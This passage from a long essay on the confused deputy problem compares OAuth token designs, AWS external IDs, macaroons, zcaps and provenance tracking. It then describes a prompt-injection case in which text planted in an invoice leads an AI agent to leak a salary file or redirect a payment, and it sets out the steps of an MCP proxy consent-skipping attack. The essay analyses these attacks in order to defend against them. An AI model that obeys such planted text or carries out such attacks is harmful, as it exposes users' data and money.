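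In a longer chain of services, the token can also list earlier actors. Jones and colleagues forbid receivers to use that history in access decisions, which may consider only the current actor and the token's main fields. Under token exchange, a suspicious service two steps back therefore appears in the record but cannot cause a refusal. IFEDAC, by contrast, lets every recorded influence restrict a request.

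The next field identifies the service meant to receive the token. If several services accept the same token, any of them can use a token it receives at the others. *OAuth Resource Indicators* (Campbell, 2020), standardised as RFC 8707, defines a way for an application to specify the service where it intends to use the token. The issuer can then make a token that only that service accepts. The Model Context Protocol, a standard for connecting AI models to tools, also relies on this restriction.

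Campbell warns that if one server hosts several customers, the address in the request must identify the customer as well as the server, or one customer could use a token to reach another's data. He also encourages applications to name a single receiver per token. But he recommends naming the base address of a whole service, so such a token usually covers every file the service holds for Alice. A 2026 draft by McGuinness and Hanson, *OAuth 2.0 Resource Parameter in Access Token Response*, lets the application detect a mix-up by having the issuer tell it which receiver the token is for.

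OAuth traditionally describes permissions with short labels, which cannot express a payment of €45 to one merchant. *OAuth 2.0 Rich Authorization Requests* (RFC 9396), by Lodderstedt, Richer and Campbell, adds a structured field that can list actions, locations and a particular resource. One example describes a payment of €123.50 to a named account. Another is a request to read the directory `/myfiles/A` and to read and write `/myfiles/A/X`.

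An entry permits every action it lists on every resource it lists, so one that lists reading and writing, and also contacts and photos, permits all four combinations. In Karp's example, a user typed the names of two files in the wrong order and overwrote the original. One entry with both files and both actions would still allow this mistake. With one entry for reading the source and another for writing the destination, the reversed copy would fail.

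The last field identifies the transaction. *Transaction Tokens* (Tulshibagwale, Fletcher and Kasselman, 2026) covers chains of services inside one organisation's network. A gateway receives a request from outside, exchanges the caller's token for a signed transaction token, and sends the new token to the first internal service. Every later service must pass it on unchanged.

In the draft's example, a customer buys 100 Microsoft shares. The token expires after six minutes and contains the customer's identifier, the permission `trade.stocks`, the action, the share's symbol, the quantity, the gateway's name and a unique transaction number. A service at the end of the chain can therefore detect that a compromised service in the middle has changed 100 shares to 10,000, but only if it compares the request with the token. The draft lets each service decide whether to make that comparison.

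Transaction tokens are not yet a standard. Tulshibagwale and colleagues issued draft 11 on 30 July 2026. The IETF working group has reached consensus on the draft and is waiting for a write-up. It aims to submit the draft in December 2026 to the steering group that approves standards.

### External IDs and SourceArn at Amazon

Amazon Web Services (AWS) uses similar information to protect its customers from confused deputies. AWS's *The confused deputy problem* describes a company, Example Corp, that monitors its customers' cloud spending. Each customer creates a role, a set of permissions in the customer's AWS account, and allows Example Corp to use it. The customer gives Example Corp the role's Amazon Resource Name (ARN).

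An ARN is not a secret, so another Example Corp customer can present the ARN of Alice's role as its own and ask for a report. Example Corp uses the role, AWS allows the request because Alice trusts Example Corp, and the other customer gets her data.

To prevent this, Example Corp assigns each customer an external ID, such as 12345 for Alice and 67890 for the other customer. Alice adds a condition to her role that requires 12345. Example Corp sends the ID of whichever customer it is working for:

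- for Alice: `f(Example Corp, 12345, use, Alice's role)` gives "yes"
- for the other customer: `f(Example Corp, 67890, use, Alice's role)` gives "no"

Unlike a password, Alice's external ID doesn't give the other customer access even if they learn it, because they cannot make Example Corp send it. AWS therefore requires Example Corp, not its customers, to choose and control the IDs.

Adding the caller's name works here because Example Corp uses Alice's role only for Alice. It did not separate the compiler's two writes because the compiler writes to BILL for every customer, so no single caller's name identifies a legitimate write. If Example Corp kept all its customers' invoices in one file, external IDs would not protect that file.

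Amazon's own services can be deputies too. CloudTrail, which records activity in an account, can write its logs to a storage area in another account. If Alice's storage area accepts logs from CloudTrail without any conditions, an outsider who knows the storage area's name can set up CloudTrail in a different account and send its logs to Alice's storage area. Alice can prevent this by requiring that CloudTrail be acting for a specific account (`aws:SourceAccount`) or a specific resource (`aws:SourceArn`).

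In its CloudTrail guide, *Cross-service confused deputy prevention*, AWS calls the full ARN the most effective protection and tells customers to use wildcards for any part they don't know. A wildcard makes the condition less precise, because every resource that matches it passes the check. Alice can also forget the condition and may not notice, because her own logs still arrive without it.

### One request with four credentials

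Consider one request: service S reads file F for user U. Here U is Alice, S is a service that writes reports, and F is her file of sales figures, which she keeps with a storage service. The report service could present any of four credentials:

1. a token that identifies only the report service
2. Alice's full token, which gives access to everything she can use
3. a token with Alice as subject, the report service as actor and the storage service as the only receiver
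4. a token that permits reading the sales file and nothing else, which Alice obtains and sends with her request

The table assumes that the report service has broad permissions of its own at the storage and email services, that each credential is a bearer token (one that works for whoever holds it), and that the report service presents no other credential.

| Misuse | 1. Service's own token | 2. Alice's full token | 3. Alice, service and receiver | 4. Sales file only |
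|---|---|---|---|---|
| Alice names Bob's salary file, which the report service may read and she may not | Allows | Stops | Stops | Stops |
| Text that Bob wrote leads the report service to read Alice's private notes | Allows | Allows | Allows | Stops |
| The report service deletes the sales file by mistake | Allows | Allows | Allows, unless the token also limits the operation | Stops |
| The storage service uses the token at Alice's email service | Allows | Allows | Stops | Stops |
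| A thief copies the token and reads the sales file | Allows | Allows | Allows | Allows |

The second credential prevents Hardy's attack by using Alice's permissions instead of the service's, but it gives the service all of her permissions. The third keeps that protection and removes the danger of reuse elsewhere. It also gives the storage service enough information to apply a special rule, such as letting the report service read only Alice's sales folder when it acts for her. Somebody has to write such a rule in advance for every service that might act for her.

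Only the fourth credential stops Bob's text from redirecting the service to Alice's notes. Bob can still influence the service, and it may try to open the notes, but the token doesn't cover them. This works because the token names the file before the service reads anything Bob wrote.

As the last row shows, a thief can use any of the four tokens until it expires, so narrowing alone does not make a stolen token useless. The damage ranges from one file with the fourth token to Alice's whole account with the second.

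### When a token becomes a capability

The fourth credential names one resource and one operation, nobody can forge it, and the service must present it with the request. It therefore fits Saltzer and Schroeder's definition of a capability. The convergence argument is that OAuth's designers started from users and their permissions and, by adding restrictions, arrived at what capability researchers had already recommended.

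People who work on digital credentials have made parts of this argument. Longley (2022) attributed the confused deputy to authorizations that give their subject a power without designating what it applies to, so the deputy has to guess or believe whoever presents the authorization. The Decentralized Identity Foundation's *Delegated Authority Evaluations v1.0 Preview* likewise concludes that designation and authorization must be combined. The foundation, an industry group, adds that the usual design, in which a service asks a central server for each access decision, still relies on identity.

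Two existing kinds of credential lie between an identity token and a pure capability. The first is the macaroon, which Birgisson, Politz and colleagues (2014), in *Macaroons*, designed for cloud services. A macaroon is a bearer token with a list of conditions that its holder can extend but not shorten. It uses an HMAC, a function that combines a key and a message into a short code that nobody can compute without the key. For a storage service with a secret key K, three successive macaroons have these codes:

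```
s0 = HMAC(K, nonce)                     any access to any chunk
s1 = HMAC(s0, "chunk in 100 to 500")    any access to those chunks
s2 = HMAC(s1, "operation is read")      reading those chunks only
```

Each macaroon contains a nonce (a random number that identifies it), its conditions and only the last code. Someone who holds `s1` can compute `s2` and give the narrower macaroon to a helper without contacting the storage service. The helper cannot compute `s1` from `s2`, so it cannot remove the read-only limit. When the helper makes a request, the storage service recomputes the codes from K and checks every condition.

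A macaroon's conditions can also restrict who may use it. Birgisson and colleagues give the example of a link to a private photo that works only for someone who can prove, through a separate service, that they are logged in and belong to a certain group. Like a capability, this macaroon both names the photo and carries the permission to access it. Madden's (2024) slides show that macaroons can carry OAuth's standard fields for permissions, receiver and expiry as conditions, so one credential can be both an OAuth token and very nearly a capability.

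The second is the authorization capability, or zcap, from the W3C Credentials Community Group's *Authorization Capabilities for Linked Data*. The group contrasts access lists, which grant authority by identity, with capabilities, which grant it by possession. Yet a zcap names the cryptographic key of the party who may use it, and that party must sign each request, so a copied zcap is useless without the key. The chain of authority starts with a root capability for each resource, and the receiver checks its own records to see who controls that resource. This check uses an access list with one or a few entries.

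After that, holders can pass on narrower versions. In the group's example, Alyssa lets her roommate Ben drive her car until she cancels the permission, and Ben lets a parking attendant drive it for at most five kilometres. The specification lags behind practice. Sporny (2023) apologised to one reader because it was out of date, and said that most of the knowledge was in the implementations.

Whether convergence supports the identity side or its critics depends on where the authority comes from. In Hardy's attack, Alice names the file BILL, but the compiler opens it with its own permission. A credential prevents this by design if whoever names a resource must also supply the authority to use it. Matt Rice described the same remedy in the thread that Miller started in 2026, saying that deputies should not use their authority on behalf of others and that users should have to provide their own.

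The token for the sales file passes this test when Alice obtains it, because she names the file by handing over the permission. An identical token can fail the test if the deputy obtains it. Suppose the compiler holds no standing permissions and must ask the issuer for a token before every write:

1. Alice names BILL as her debugging file.
2. The compiler asks the issuer, under its own identity, for a token to write to BILL.
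3. The issuer finds that the compiler may write to BILL and issues a token for that file and operation only.
4. The compiler presents the token and overwrites the billing records.

The attack works even though the token is as narrow as possible. The issuer decided `f(compiler, write, BILL)`, so Hardy's problem has only moved from the file system to the issuer. If the compiler had sent Alice's token with its request, the issuer could have refused, but the compiler's programmer would then have to remember which identity to use, as with impersonation. Narrow tokens prevent the confusion only when the same party chooses the resource and supplies the authority.

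According to Karp, the trouble arises when a receiver uses someone's authenticated identity, role or attributes to look up their permissions. The third credential in the table still works this way, because the storage service looks up what Alice may do. The fourth doesn't, because the permission is in the token. The issuer used Alice's identity earlier to decide that she could have the token, much as Unix checks a user's identity when it opens a file and then relies on the descriptor.

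Anyone who defends identity-based checks by offering the fourth credential as an answer to Hardy has therefore conceded that a capability should control the use of the file. Identity is still important for deciding who gets the capability. This is consistent with the case for capabilities, since someone always has to decide who receives a capability first.

External IDs better support the case for identity-based checks. The customer who names Alice's role supplies no authority of its own, so the arrangement fails the test, yet AWS stops the attack by checking who that customer is. This identity-based check prevents a confused deputy when the deputy reports its caller correctly and each resource belongs to the one caller who may name it. Many cloud services meet both conditions, but the compiler does not meet the second.

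### The costs of narrow credentials

A bearer token that leaks works for whoever finds it. Tulshibagwale and colleagues acknowledge that a thief can replay a transaction token until it expires. A service can remember each transaction number and refuse to accept it twice, but this may not be feasible when many copies of the service run without shared records. Jones and colleagues warn that if an issuer doesn't require services to authenticate when they exchange tokens, anyone with a stolen token can exchange it for others. Zcaps avoid the problem of copied tokens by requiring a signature, but every holder then has to protect a key.

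Revoking permissions is simpler with an access list than with token exchange. Once an administrator deletes Alice's entry, her next access check fails. With token exchange, the new token has no lasting link to the old one, so revoking Alice's original token doesn't automatically revoke tokens that services have already obtained with it. If the issuer's policy allows it, a transaction token may even stay valid after the token that the gateway exchanged for it expires.

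Designers mostly respond by making tokens short-lived. Birgisson and colleagues list three other methods: requiring fresh evidence with each request, consulting an outside record such as a list of cancelled credentials, and splitting a credential so that its holder must keep collecting a new part. Consulting an outside record brings back a lookup for every request. For zcaps, the W3C Credentials Community Group requires receivers to remember each cancelled capability until it expires, and so recommends that they reject any capability that expires more than three months away.

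A capability that names only a file leaves no record of who used it, so identity fields are useful even when they play no part in the access decision. If every service logs the transaction number, an investigator can reconstruct what happened to a request. The subject and actor fields show for whom a service acted. McGuinness (2026), in *OAuth Actor Profile for Delegation*, notes that existing standards lack a consistent way to represent actors across token types, which makes it harder to follow a request from one organisation to another.

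The hardest practical question is who issues a token for each action. In the scheme that Lodderstedt and colleagues describe, the issuer shows the user the requested details and asks for consent, which suits a single payment. The IETF draft *Txn Challenge* (2026) covers a related case, in which a caller's token is valid but the receiver needs separate approval for one specific operation.

Approving 10,000 files one by one for a nightly backup is impractical. Alice could instead give the backup service a token for the whole folder, but the service could then use any file in it for the wrong purpose. Or the service could request a token for each file without her approval, but the issuer would again be relying on the service to report what she wanted.

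Macaroons let the backup service easily narrow a folder token to one file by itself. This protects Alice from whatever the service calls next, but not from the service itself acting as a confused deputy, because the service chooses the file.

For ordinary files, the easiest time to issue a narrow credential is when the user picks the file, since she has to name it anyway. If Alice's command shell or file chooser passes a token along with the name, she never sees a separate request for consent.

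A transaction token can contain the gateway's mistakes, because the gateway describes the request to the issuer, which may copy the details into the token. If the gateway identifies the wrong account, the issuer may sign that account number. Later services can verify that nobody has altered the token, but that check won't reveal that the user meant a different account.

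## What capabilities do not prevent

Alice's token for the sales file keeps Bob's text from getting the report service to read her private notes. But if she also gives the service permission to write one report, it could still put a false figure from Bob's text in that report. The report would then be wrong even though the service used only the files Alice chose.

In 2016, Rajani and colleagues examined such attacks by writing ten small programs, five containing an attack and five harmless. They worked out how each would fare under access control, capabilities and two versions of provenance tracking, which labels values with the principals who influenced them and checks the labels before use.

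### A test for both sides

Programs in the model's language can do little more than read and write memory locations, branch and loop. The language ranks principals by trust, and every location has an owner. A program runs as a series of blocks, each with the authority of one principal, and a block may change a location only if its principal ranks at least as high as the owner. Code also needs a read reference to read a location and a write reference to change it. Any principal that has a read reference may use it, so the model covers damage to data but not theft.

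The capability rules check permission when code obtains a write reference, so they have to inspect every value that code computes or reads. Rajani and colleagues compare this to a barrier in Firefox that intercepts objects passing from one website's code to another's. They concede that checking every value takes a lot of computation, and treat their rules as an idealised capability system.

To test a program, they leave one block empty for the attacker's code. The program is free of confused deputy attacks if, for each protected location that the attacker wants to change, at least one of these is true:

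1. The attacker has no control over the location. Whatever code goes into the empty block, the location ends up with the same value.
2. The attacker didn't need a deputy. Some code running with only the attacker's authority could have left that value there.

The definition does not depend on who named the location, so it is closer to Miller, Yee and Shapiro's broad definition than to Karp's narrow one. It is weaker than the usual standard for data integrity, which forbids untrusted data from affecting trusted data at all. A program that copies an untrusted location into a trusted one fails that standard but passes under this definition if it has no block for an attacker to fill.

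### Four attacks

Here is the deputy's code in the first four programs, rewritten in terms of the compiler. Alice, the attacker, can write to OUT, SOURCE, NOTE, FLAG and SLOT, but not to BILL. SLOT already contains a reference to BILL when the program starts.

```
1.  location named in OUT  := compile(SOURCE)
2.  BILL                   := NOTE
3.  if FLAG then BILL := 41 else BILL := 42
4.  location named in SLOT := NOTE
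```

Program 1 is Hardy's attack, which access control allows. Under the capability rules, OUT can hold only references that Alice could have used herself, so the attack fails.

In program 2, Alice never handles a reference to BILL. The deputy has one in its own code and uses it to copy whatever she wrote in NOTE into BILL. If she writes 42, BILL ends up containing 42. She controls the value in BILL but could not have written it there herself, so both parts of the definition fail. Rajani and colleagues liken this to SQL injection, in which text that an outsider types into a web form ends up inside a database command.

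Alice has even less influence in program 3, where both numbers belong to the deputy and she sets only a flag that chooses between them. But if the numbers are prices, that is all the influence she needs.

In program 4, Alice changes NOTE but not SLOT. The deputy follows the reference in SLOT and writes her text to BILL.

Rajani and colleagues call the designation explicit when the deputy gets the reference from the attacker, as in program 1. They call it implicit when the deputy already has the reference, or finds it in memory, and the attacker influences what the deputy writes. Capabilities stop the explicit attack, but the other three succeed under the capability rules.

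Program 4 is the weakest of these as evidence against capabilities, because it depends on a design choice in the model. In an ordinary object-capability system, holding a reference is permission to use it, so if Alice could read SLOT, she could take the reference and write to BILL herself. That would be a leaked capability, not a confused deputy. The model instead checks each reference against a separate policy, so it halts Alice if she reads SLOT but lets the deputy read it. Rajani and colleagues chose this so that an accidental leak would count as a violation. Programs 2 and 3 don't depend on that choice, since a deputy may legitimately hold its reference to BILL.

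### Endorsing the bill

Taken literally, the definition makes an honest compiler's ordinary billing an attack, because the charge it writes to BILL depends on source code from Alice, who is not allowed to write to that file. The causal definition in *Proof-of-Continuity* has the same problem.

Rajani and colleagues fix this with endorsement. A programmer can mark a block as one that may act on another principal's behalf, and the test then applies only to the code between marked blocks. In their program 5, the full compiler, the block that writes the bill is endorsed and the block that writes the compiled code is not. The program still fails the test because Alice can name BILL as her output file, but writing the charge no longer contributes to the failure.

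An endorsed block still needs permission to write to the location. Endorsing the block only declares that outsiders may influence what it writes, whereas Fournet and Gordon's `grant` restores a permission that the caller lacks.

The exemption covers everything in an endorsed block. If an odd comment in Alice's source code makes the billing formula in such a block return zero, the definition doesn't count the false charge as an attack. A programmer who put both of the compiler's writes in one endorsed block would also exempt Hardy's attack.

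### Labelling every value

Both provenance systems start from the access control rules and add a label to each value, showing the least trusted principal whose data went into it. The simpler version tracks only direct copying and reading:

1. A constant in the program's code gets the most trusted label.
2. A value that code reads from a location gets the label of the location's owner, or a lower one if the reference used to read it had a lower label.
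3. Before a write, the system checks the block's permission as usual. It then checks that the labels on the reference and on the value both rank at least as high as the location's owner. Endorsed blocks skip this second check.

In the compiler, a reference to BILL that arrives through OUT carries Alice's label because she owns OUT. She ranks below BILL's owner, so the system refuses the write. The billing code's own reference to BILL is a constant and passes the check. The amount of the charge doesn't pass because the compiler calculates it from Alice's source code, so the billing block needs an endorsement.

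The system therefore distinguishes the compiler's two writes only by the label on the reference. A weaker version that checked only that label would refuse the debugging output and allow the charge without endorsement. IFEDAC could not do this because it kept one set of influences for the whole process.

Partial tracking misses the attack in program 3 because 41 and 42 are constants with the most trusted label, and the system ignores the flag that determines which one is used. Full tracking adds a label for the program's current position. When the program enters a branch or loop, the system lowers this label to match the condition's, and restores the old label when the program leaves. A write to BILL inside a branch that depends on Alice's flag then fails.

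Hardy's exercise concerns a check that uses the requester, the operation and the resource. These systems add more identities to that check and keep an ordinary policy about who may write where. Full tracking stops all five attacks, including three that succeed against capabilities, which bears on whether identity-based checks fail in principle.

The comparison makes access control look somewhat better than it is. The extra protection comes from the labels, which, as far as the argument shows, a designer could also add to a capability system. The labels exist only because the language tracks every value from one step to the next. A file server that receives a name from another machine gets no label with it unless both machines take part in the tracking.

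### What each system stops and what it guarantees

| Program | Attack? | Access control | Capabilities | Partial tracking | Full tracking |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| 1. Attacker names the output location | Yes | Allows | Stops | Stops | Stops |
| 2. Attacker supplies the value | Yes | Allows | No guarantee | Stops | Stops |
| 3. Attacker steers a branch | Yes | Allows | No guarantee | No guarantee | Stops |
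| 4. Deputy finds a dangerous reference in the attacker's slot | Yes | Allows | No guarantee | Stops | Stops |
| 5. Full compiler with endorsed billing | Yes | Allows | Stops | Stops | Stops |
| 6. Deputy writes the constant 1 to a protected location | No | Runs | No guarantee | No guarantee | Runs |
| 7. Code copies a protected reference between unprotected locations | No | Runs | No guarantee | Runs | Runs |
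| 8. Code copies a value from a less trusted location to a more trusted one | No | Runs | Runs | Blocks | Blocks |
| 9. Code copies a protected reference between protected locations | No | Runs | No guarantee | No guarantee | Runs |
| 10. A less trusted value decides what code writes to a more trusted location | No | Runs | Runs | Runs | Blocks |

"No guarantee" means that the program breaks the conditions under which Rajani and colleagues could prove the system safe. The system may still run the program. Partial tracking, for example, runs program 6 to completion. Capabilities do so only if the attacker's code doesn't try to obtain a forbidden reference. If it does, the rules halt the whole program before the deputy runs.

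Three theorems state the conditions. Each promises freedom from confused deputy attacks outside endorsed blocks:

- **Theorem 4, capabilities.** When the program starts, no location in memory may contain a write reference to a protected location that the attacker wants. Trusted code outside endorsed blocks may not contain one either.
- **Theorem 5, partial tracking.** The condition on code stays the same, but the condition on memory applies only to protected locations. Locations that the attacker can write to may contain dangerous references, because anything read from them gets a low label.
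- **Theorem 6, full tracking.** There are no conditions.

A deputy can get a dangerous reference from its own code, from memory or from the attacker. The capability rules block the last source, and the two conditions of Theorem 4 block the others, so nobody ever writes to the locations at risk. Rajani and colleagues say that these restrictions make the language "useless for almost all practical purposes". That is a little harsh, because the full compiler meets both conditions and endorsed blocks may hold dangerous references. But the theorem doesn't cover endorsed blocks.

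Stronger protection also blocks some harmless programs. Programs 8 and 10 contain no attacker's code, but full tracking blocks both because a less trusted value affects a more trusted location. The same thing happens whenever a trusted program reads its settings from a file that ordinary users can edit, and the programmer would have to endorse each such case. Partial tracking blocks only program 8, and Rajani and colleagues expect it to run far more efficiently than full tracking.

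### Whether a wrong value makes a confused deputy

Capability researchers can answer that programs 2 and 3 aren't confused deputies. Karp's definition requires somebody else to choose the resource, and in both programs the deputy itself chose BILL.

*Is this a confused deputy?* (Karp, 2025) illustrates this distinction with Alice, who keeps a file for each letter of the alphabet and adds each word to the files for the letters it contains. Bob's service tells her which files to update. A malicious Bob can name some other file, and Alice will use her own permissions to overwrite it. Karp's solution is for Alice to give Bob a capability for each letter file, so that he can designate only those files.

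Mike Stay, another participant, pointed out that Bob could still get "cab" added to the file for Z. To prevent this, the capabilities would have to enforce the rule about letters as well as designate the files, and Alice could forget to build that in. Karp replied that his concern was whether Bob could make Alice write to a file she didn't want written. He considered wrong contents a matter for the application, which he wanted to keep separate from access control. Stay agreed that capabilities solve the problem Karp had posed.

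Karp's line is a reasonable way to divide responsibility, since no general-purpose permission system can determine which words contain a Z. It also narrows the claim for capabilities. They stop outsiders from choosing a resource they aren't allowed to use, but the deputy's programmer must handle everything else an outsider can influence.

This line can be hard to apply to SQL injection. Program 2 fixes the location and lets the attacker supply only a value. In real attacks, the attacker's text can also name a different table in the database. The attacker then designates the resource and the web server supplies the permission, which makes the server a confused deputy even by Karp's definition. Capabilities would stop this if the server had a separate one for each table it needed, but a server with a single reference to the whole database would still let the text pick any table. Slides from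 a 2025 workshop run by LangSec, a group that studies security flaws in how programs handle input, simply classify SQL injection as a confused deputy.

Nicol (2026), in *Permity*, proposed new words for permission and authority, and the replies help explain why the two definitions differ. Karp gave the example of a web server, where a visitor has no permission to read the home page file but has the authority to see its contents because the server reads it for them. Authority in this sense includes whatever someone can bring about through others. Under Rajani and colleagues' definition, any such indirect power over a protected location is an attack unless a programmer has endorsed it. In the same discussion, Miller described the confused deputy as one of many bugs that give someone more authority than intended. Applying his view requires some record of what people intended, and endorsement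 is one such record.

### Keys, boxes and maps

Defenders of capabilities also reply that they never promised complete safety. Miller and colleagues wrote in 2003 that removing ambient authority "doesn't guarantee that deputies will never be confused", and gave the example of the deputy who tries every key. Rajani and colleagues read a diagram in that paper as suggesting that confused deputy attacks are impossible under Property A, where naming a resource always conveys permission to use it. The paper's text makes this claim only for attackers who name an off-limits resource, and programs 1 and 5 support that narrower claim.

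Even this narrower claim depends on programmers keeping names and permissions together, and capability systems give them ways to separate the two. One is the sealed box, which anyone can hold or pass on, but which contains a capability that only a program with the matching "unsealer" can use. In the mailing-list thread that Karp started in 2019, Christopher Lemmer Webber warned about a deputy that keeps several unsealers and tries each one until the box opens. Miller explained that this is dangerous because Alice, by choosing the box, chooses which authority the deputy will use from a set she can't use herself.

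Karp first asked where the confused deputy was. Kevin Reid described a compiler that has an unsealer meant for billing accounts and uses it on a box that Alice supplied as her output file. As with the keys, Reid's remedy is that the deputy has to remember what each unsealer is for. Karp then accepted Webber's point.

Webber also described an attack in which the deputy doesn't search a bucket. A bot rewrites blog posts with silly capitalization and sends the result to whoever asked. A blogger who likes the bot gives it the means to open every post, including private ones. Visitors can see that a private post exists but can't open it. If a visitor points the bot at one, the bot opens it and sends them the rewritten text. The system has no access lists, but the attack still fits Karp's definition of a confused deputy, because the visitor designated the post and the bot used its own permission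 to open it.

Capability researchers use the term "rights amplification" for combining a box with an unsealer to get a power that neither gives alone. Miller agreed that rights amplification makes confused deputies possible, but he thought it unlikely to cause one by accident.

Karp (2026), in *Confused deputy*, asked whether anyone had proved that a capability system cannot express the vulnerability. William Leslie answered that such a system can express it. A deputy can put its capabilities in a table that pairs names with capabilities and let the client choose an entry. Leslie added that if the deputy uses only capabilities that the client provides, the client must already have had the authority.

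Miller gave a similar condition. The 2003 paper's argument covers deputies that designate resources only with capabilities, which he called a severe restriction that many normal deputies don't meet. He expects most of those deputies to be safe anyway, although the argument can't prove it. His rule of thumb is that a deputy is probably safe if it avoids rights amplification. Miller's condition limits how a deputy refers to things, unlike Theorem 4, which limits the references it holds. Both leave a good deal of ordinary code without a guarantee.

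Developers can easily build Leslie's map without noticing. A bank's program has one if it takes an account number from a customer and looks up the capability for that account. The bank could avoid the map by giving customers capabilities instead of account numbers. If it keeps the numbers, the program has to check whether the customer may use that account, which is an identity-based check.

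## Agents that use their user's identity

When a customer gives a bank an account number, the bank can check whether that customer may use the account. The check works because the customer chose the number. When an AI agent makes the request on the customer's behalf, the number may come from an email that a stranger wrote, but the bank still checks whether the customer may use the account.

### How agents get access

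Developers usually authorize an agent in one of three ways, and each gives the receiving service different information.

| Arrangement | Example | Whom the service sees |
|---|---|---|
| The user's own session | An agent works in a browser where Alice has already logged in, or uses the keys stored on her laptop | Alice |
| A delegated token | Alice approves the agent on a consent screen, and it receives an OAuth token | Alice, and also the agent if the token has an actor field |
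| The agent's own account | A company gives the agent a service account or an API key | The agent, or only the key |

When the agent uses Alice's session, the service can't tell whether she or the agent clicked a button. Agents that operate a screen also bypass the controls that services build into their programming interfaces, according to *Identity Management for Agentic AI* (South, 2025), a whitepaper for the OpenID Foundation, which develops login standards.

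When an agent uses its own account, the service can identify the agent but not the person it is working for. A static API key reveals even less, because anyone who has it can use it. *Authorization Architectures for Tool-Using AI Agents* notes that with such a key, the service can't distinguish the intended agent from one that an attacker has taken over.

A delegated token can identify both the user and the agent. But *AI Identity* (2026) warns that developers who apply OAuth to agents without changing it end up either replaying the user's own token or handing out broad API keys. An ordinary OAuth scope such as `email.send` also doesn't limit who receives the email, what it contains or which task it serves.

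### One invoice, two attacks

Alice tells her agent to pay an invoice from a printing firm and to reply once it has paid. The agent can read her email and files, send messages and make payments from her account. Bob has broken into the firm's mailbox and added text to the invoice.

- In form A, the text leads the agent to attach Alice's private salary file to its reply, which Bob then reads.
- In form B, the text replaces the firm's account number with Bob's, and the agent pays him.

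In form A, Bob names a file that he isn't allowed to read, and the agent opens it using Alice's right to read it. That makes the agent a confused deputy even under Karp's narrow definition. In form B, Bob names only his own account, which he is allowed to use. The agent is a confused deputy only under the broad definition, because Bob has manipulated it into misusing Alice's authority over her money.

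| Check | Form A | Form B |
|---|---|---|
| Impersonation of Alice | Allows | Allows |
| The agent's own account, without access to the salary file | Stops | Allows |
| Tracking the chain of callers | Allows | Allows |
| Tracking whose data the agent has read | Stops | Stops, but also blocks the honest payment |
| Checking the origin | Allows | Allows |
| A token for this job, with the account number from the invoice | Stops | Allows |
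| A token for this job, with the account number from Alice's records | Stops | Stops |

Impersonation does not stop Bob because he never calls any service himself. The file service evaluates f(Alice, read, salary file) and the bank evaluates f(Alice, pay, Alice's account). Both checks pass, as they would if Alice had made the requests herself. If the agent has its own account, the file service refuses unless someone has shared the salary file with the agent. The bank still makes the payment, because making payments is the agent's job.

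Tracking callers adds the agent's name to Alice's but leaves out Bob, because he only wrote some text. A system like IFEDAC, which also records whose data a process has read, would mark the agent as influenced by an outsider as soon as it opened the invoice. The system would then stop the agent from opening the salary file or paying Bob. It would also block the honest payment, since the printing firm may not spend Alice's money either. Making an exception for payments would allow both.

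Origin checks don't help because no other website is involved. An agent that calls the bank's programming interface directly usually sends no origin. A browser agent fills in the form on the bank's own page, so the bank receives its own origin.

Suppose Alice's request-scoped token lets the agent read this message, send one reply and make one payment. Form A fails because the token doesn't cover the salary file. Whether form B succeeds depends on where the account number comes from. If the agent reads the invoice and then requests a token for the payment, the issuer receives Bob's number and signs it. If the number comes from Alice's records of earlier payments to the firm, the bank refuses to pay Bob.

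The issuer could also ask Alice for approval. South describes a standard called CIBA (Client-Initiated Backchannel Authentication), which sends the request to the user's own device while the agent continues working. The request can describe the payment. But Alice probably doesn't know the firm's account number by heart, and if she checks the invoice, she will find the same wrong number there. *Authorization Architectures* recommends that such prompts also show which sources influenced the request. That would help Alice if the agent's software could identify those sources reliably.

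With Bob's number in it, a token for the payment could contain:

```
user:      Alice
agent:     Alice's agent
receiver:  the bank
action:    pay €1,800
payee:     Bob's account number
```

Every identity here is correct. The agent works for Alice, the bank is the intended receiver, and the payee is the account the agent asked it to pay. The payment is wrong only because Alice meant to pay the printing firm, and the bank has no record of that.

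### Checking the payee

Common software for building agents doesn't check by default whether such values are permitted. *Capability Gates Are Not Authorization* (Mellafe Zuvic, 2026) reports an audit of the public code of LangChain (with its companion LangGraph), LlamaIndex and the payment company Stripe's toolkit for agents. All three had "capability gates", which decide which tools an agent can call, but none checked the values in a call by default before running it. These gates don't involve unforgeable references. In a test with a mock shop, LangChain ran a call that redirected the shop's payouts to an attacker's account.

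Mellafe Zuvic's remedy, ScopeGate, compares each call with limits and lists of approved values the operator has set. It refused the payout call because the attacker's account was not on the list. It also refused 48 prepared attempts to get past it, and all 29 unauthorized calls from an attacker model that could see why earlier calls had failed. It allowed all ten harmless calls in the test. An earlier version had a bug that let through a payment whose amount was "not a number", a special value computers use for invalid results.

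This check would stop form B if the printing firm's account is on the list and Bob's is not. It works regardless of who wrote the invoice or why the agent chose the number. But the list must come from a source that the model can't influence, and somebody has to add each new supplier. The check also can't prevent the agent from paying the wrong supplier on the list.

The choice of model affects how often a gate has to block a harmful action. In a companion test of 27 models, the injected text presented the harmful action as part of the user's task. The 12 cheaper models attempted it 60% of the time on average and the 15 flagship models 19%, while Gemini 3.1 Pro never attempted it.

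### The Model Context Protocol's rules

Many agents reach their tools through the Model Context Protocol (MCP), in which an AI application, called the client, connects to servers that offer tools. MCP's original design had no authentication. Its current rules, in *Authorization* (2026), date from 28 July 2026 and build on OAuth.

Authorization is optional under these rules. They also exclude servers that run on the user's own machine and exchange text with the client directly. Such a server takes its credentials from its surroundings, which may mean whatever keys the user has stored there. For servers that clients reach over the web and that support authorization, there are three main requirements:

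- The client must name the server for which it wants a token.
- The server must check that the issuer made the token for that server, and reject any other token.
- If the server calls another service, it must use a separate token from that service's issuer. It must not pass on the client's token.

The ban on passing tokens through protects the service that would receive them. The Model Context Protocol's *Security Best Practices* explains that this service might otherwise assume the server had already checked the token. Its logs could also attribute the requests to the wrong source, and a thief could use the server to relay stolen tokens. The protocol's *Authorization Security Considerations* (2026) adds that tying tokens to one receiver works only if the issuer supports it.

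MCP's own confused deputy is a proxy server, which connects many clients to one outside service. Suppose a proxy connects AI applications to Alice's storage service, where the proxy has registered under a single fixed identity. The attack goes as follows:

1. Alice connects her usual application through the proxy. The storage service asks for her consent and saves a cookie in her browser recording that she has approved the proxy.
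2. An attacker registers a client of their own with the proxy and gives an address that the attacker controls for its replies.
3. The attacker sends Alice a link that starts the authorization process for this new client.
4. Alice clicks the link. The storage service finds the cookie and skips the consent screen.
5. The proxy sends an authorization code to the attacker's address. The attacker exchanges it for a token and can now use Alice's storage through the proxy.

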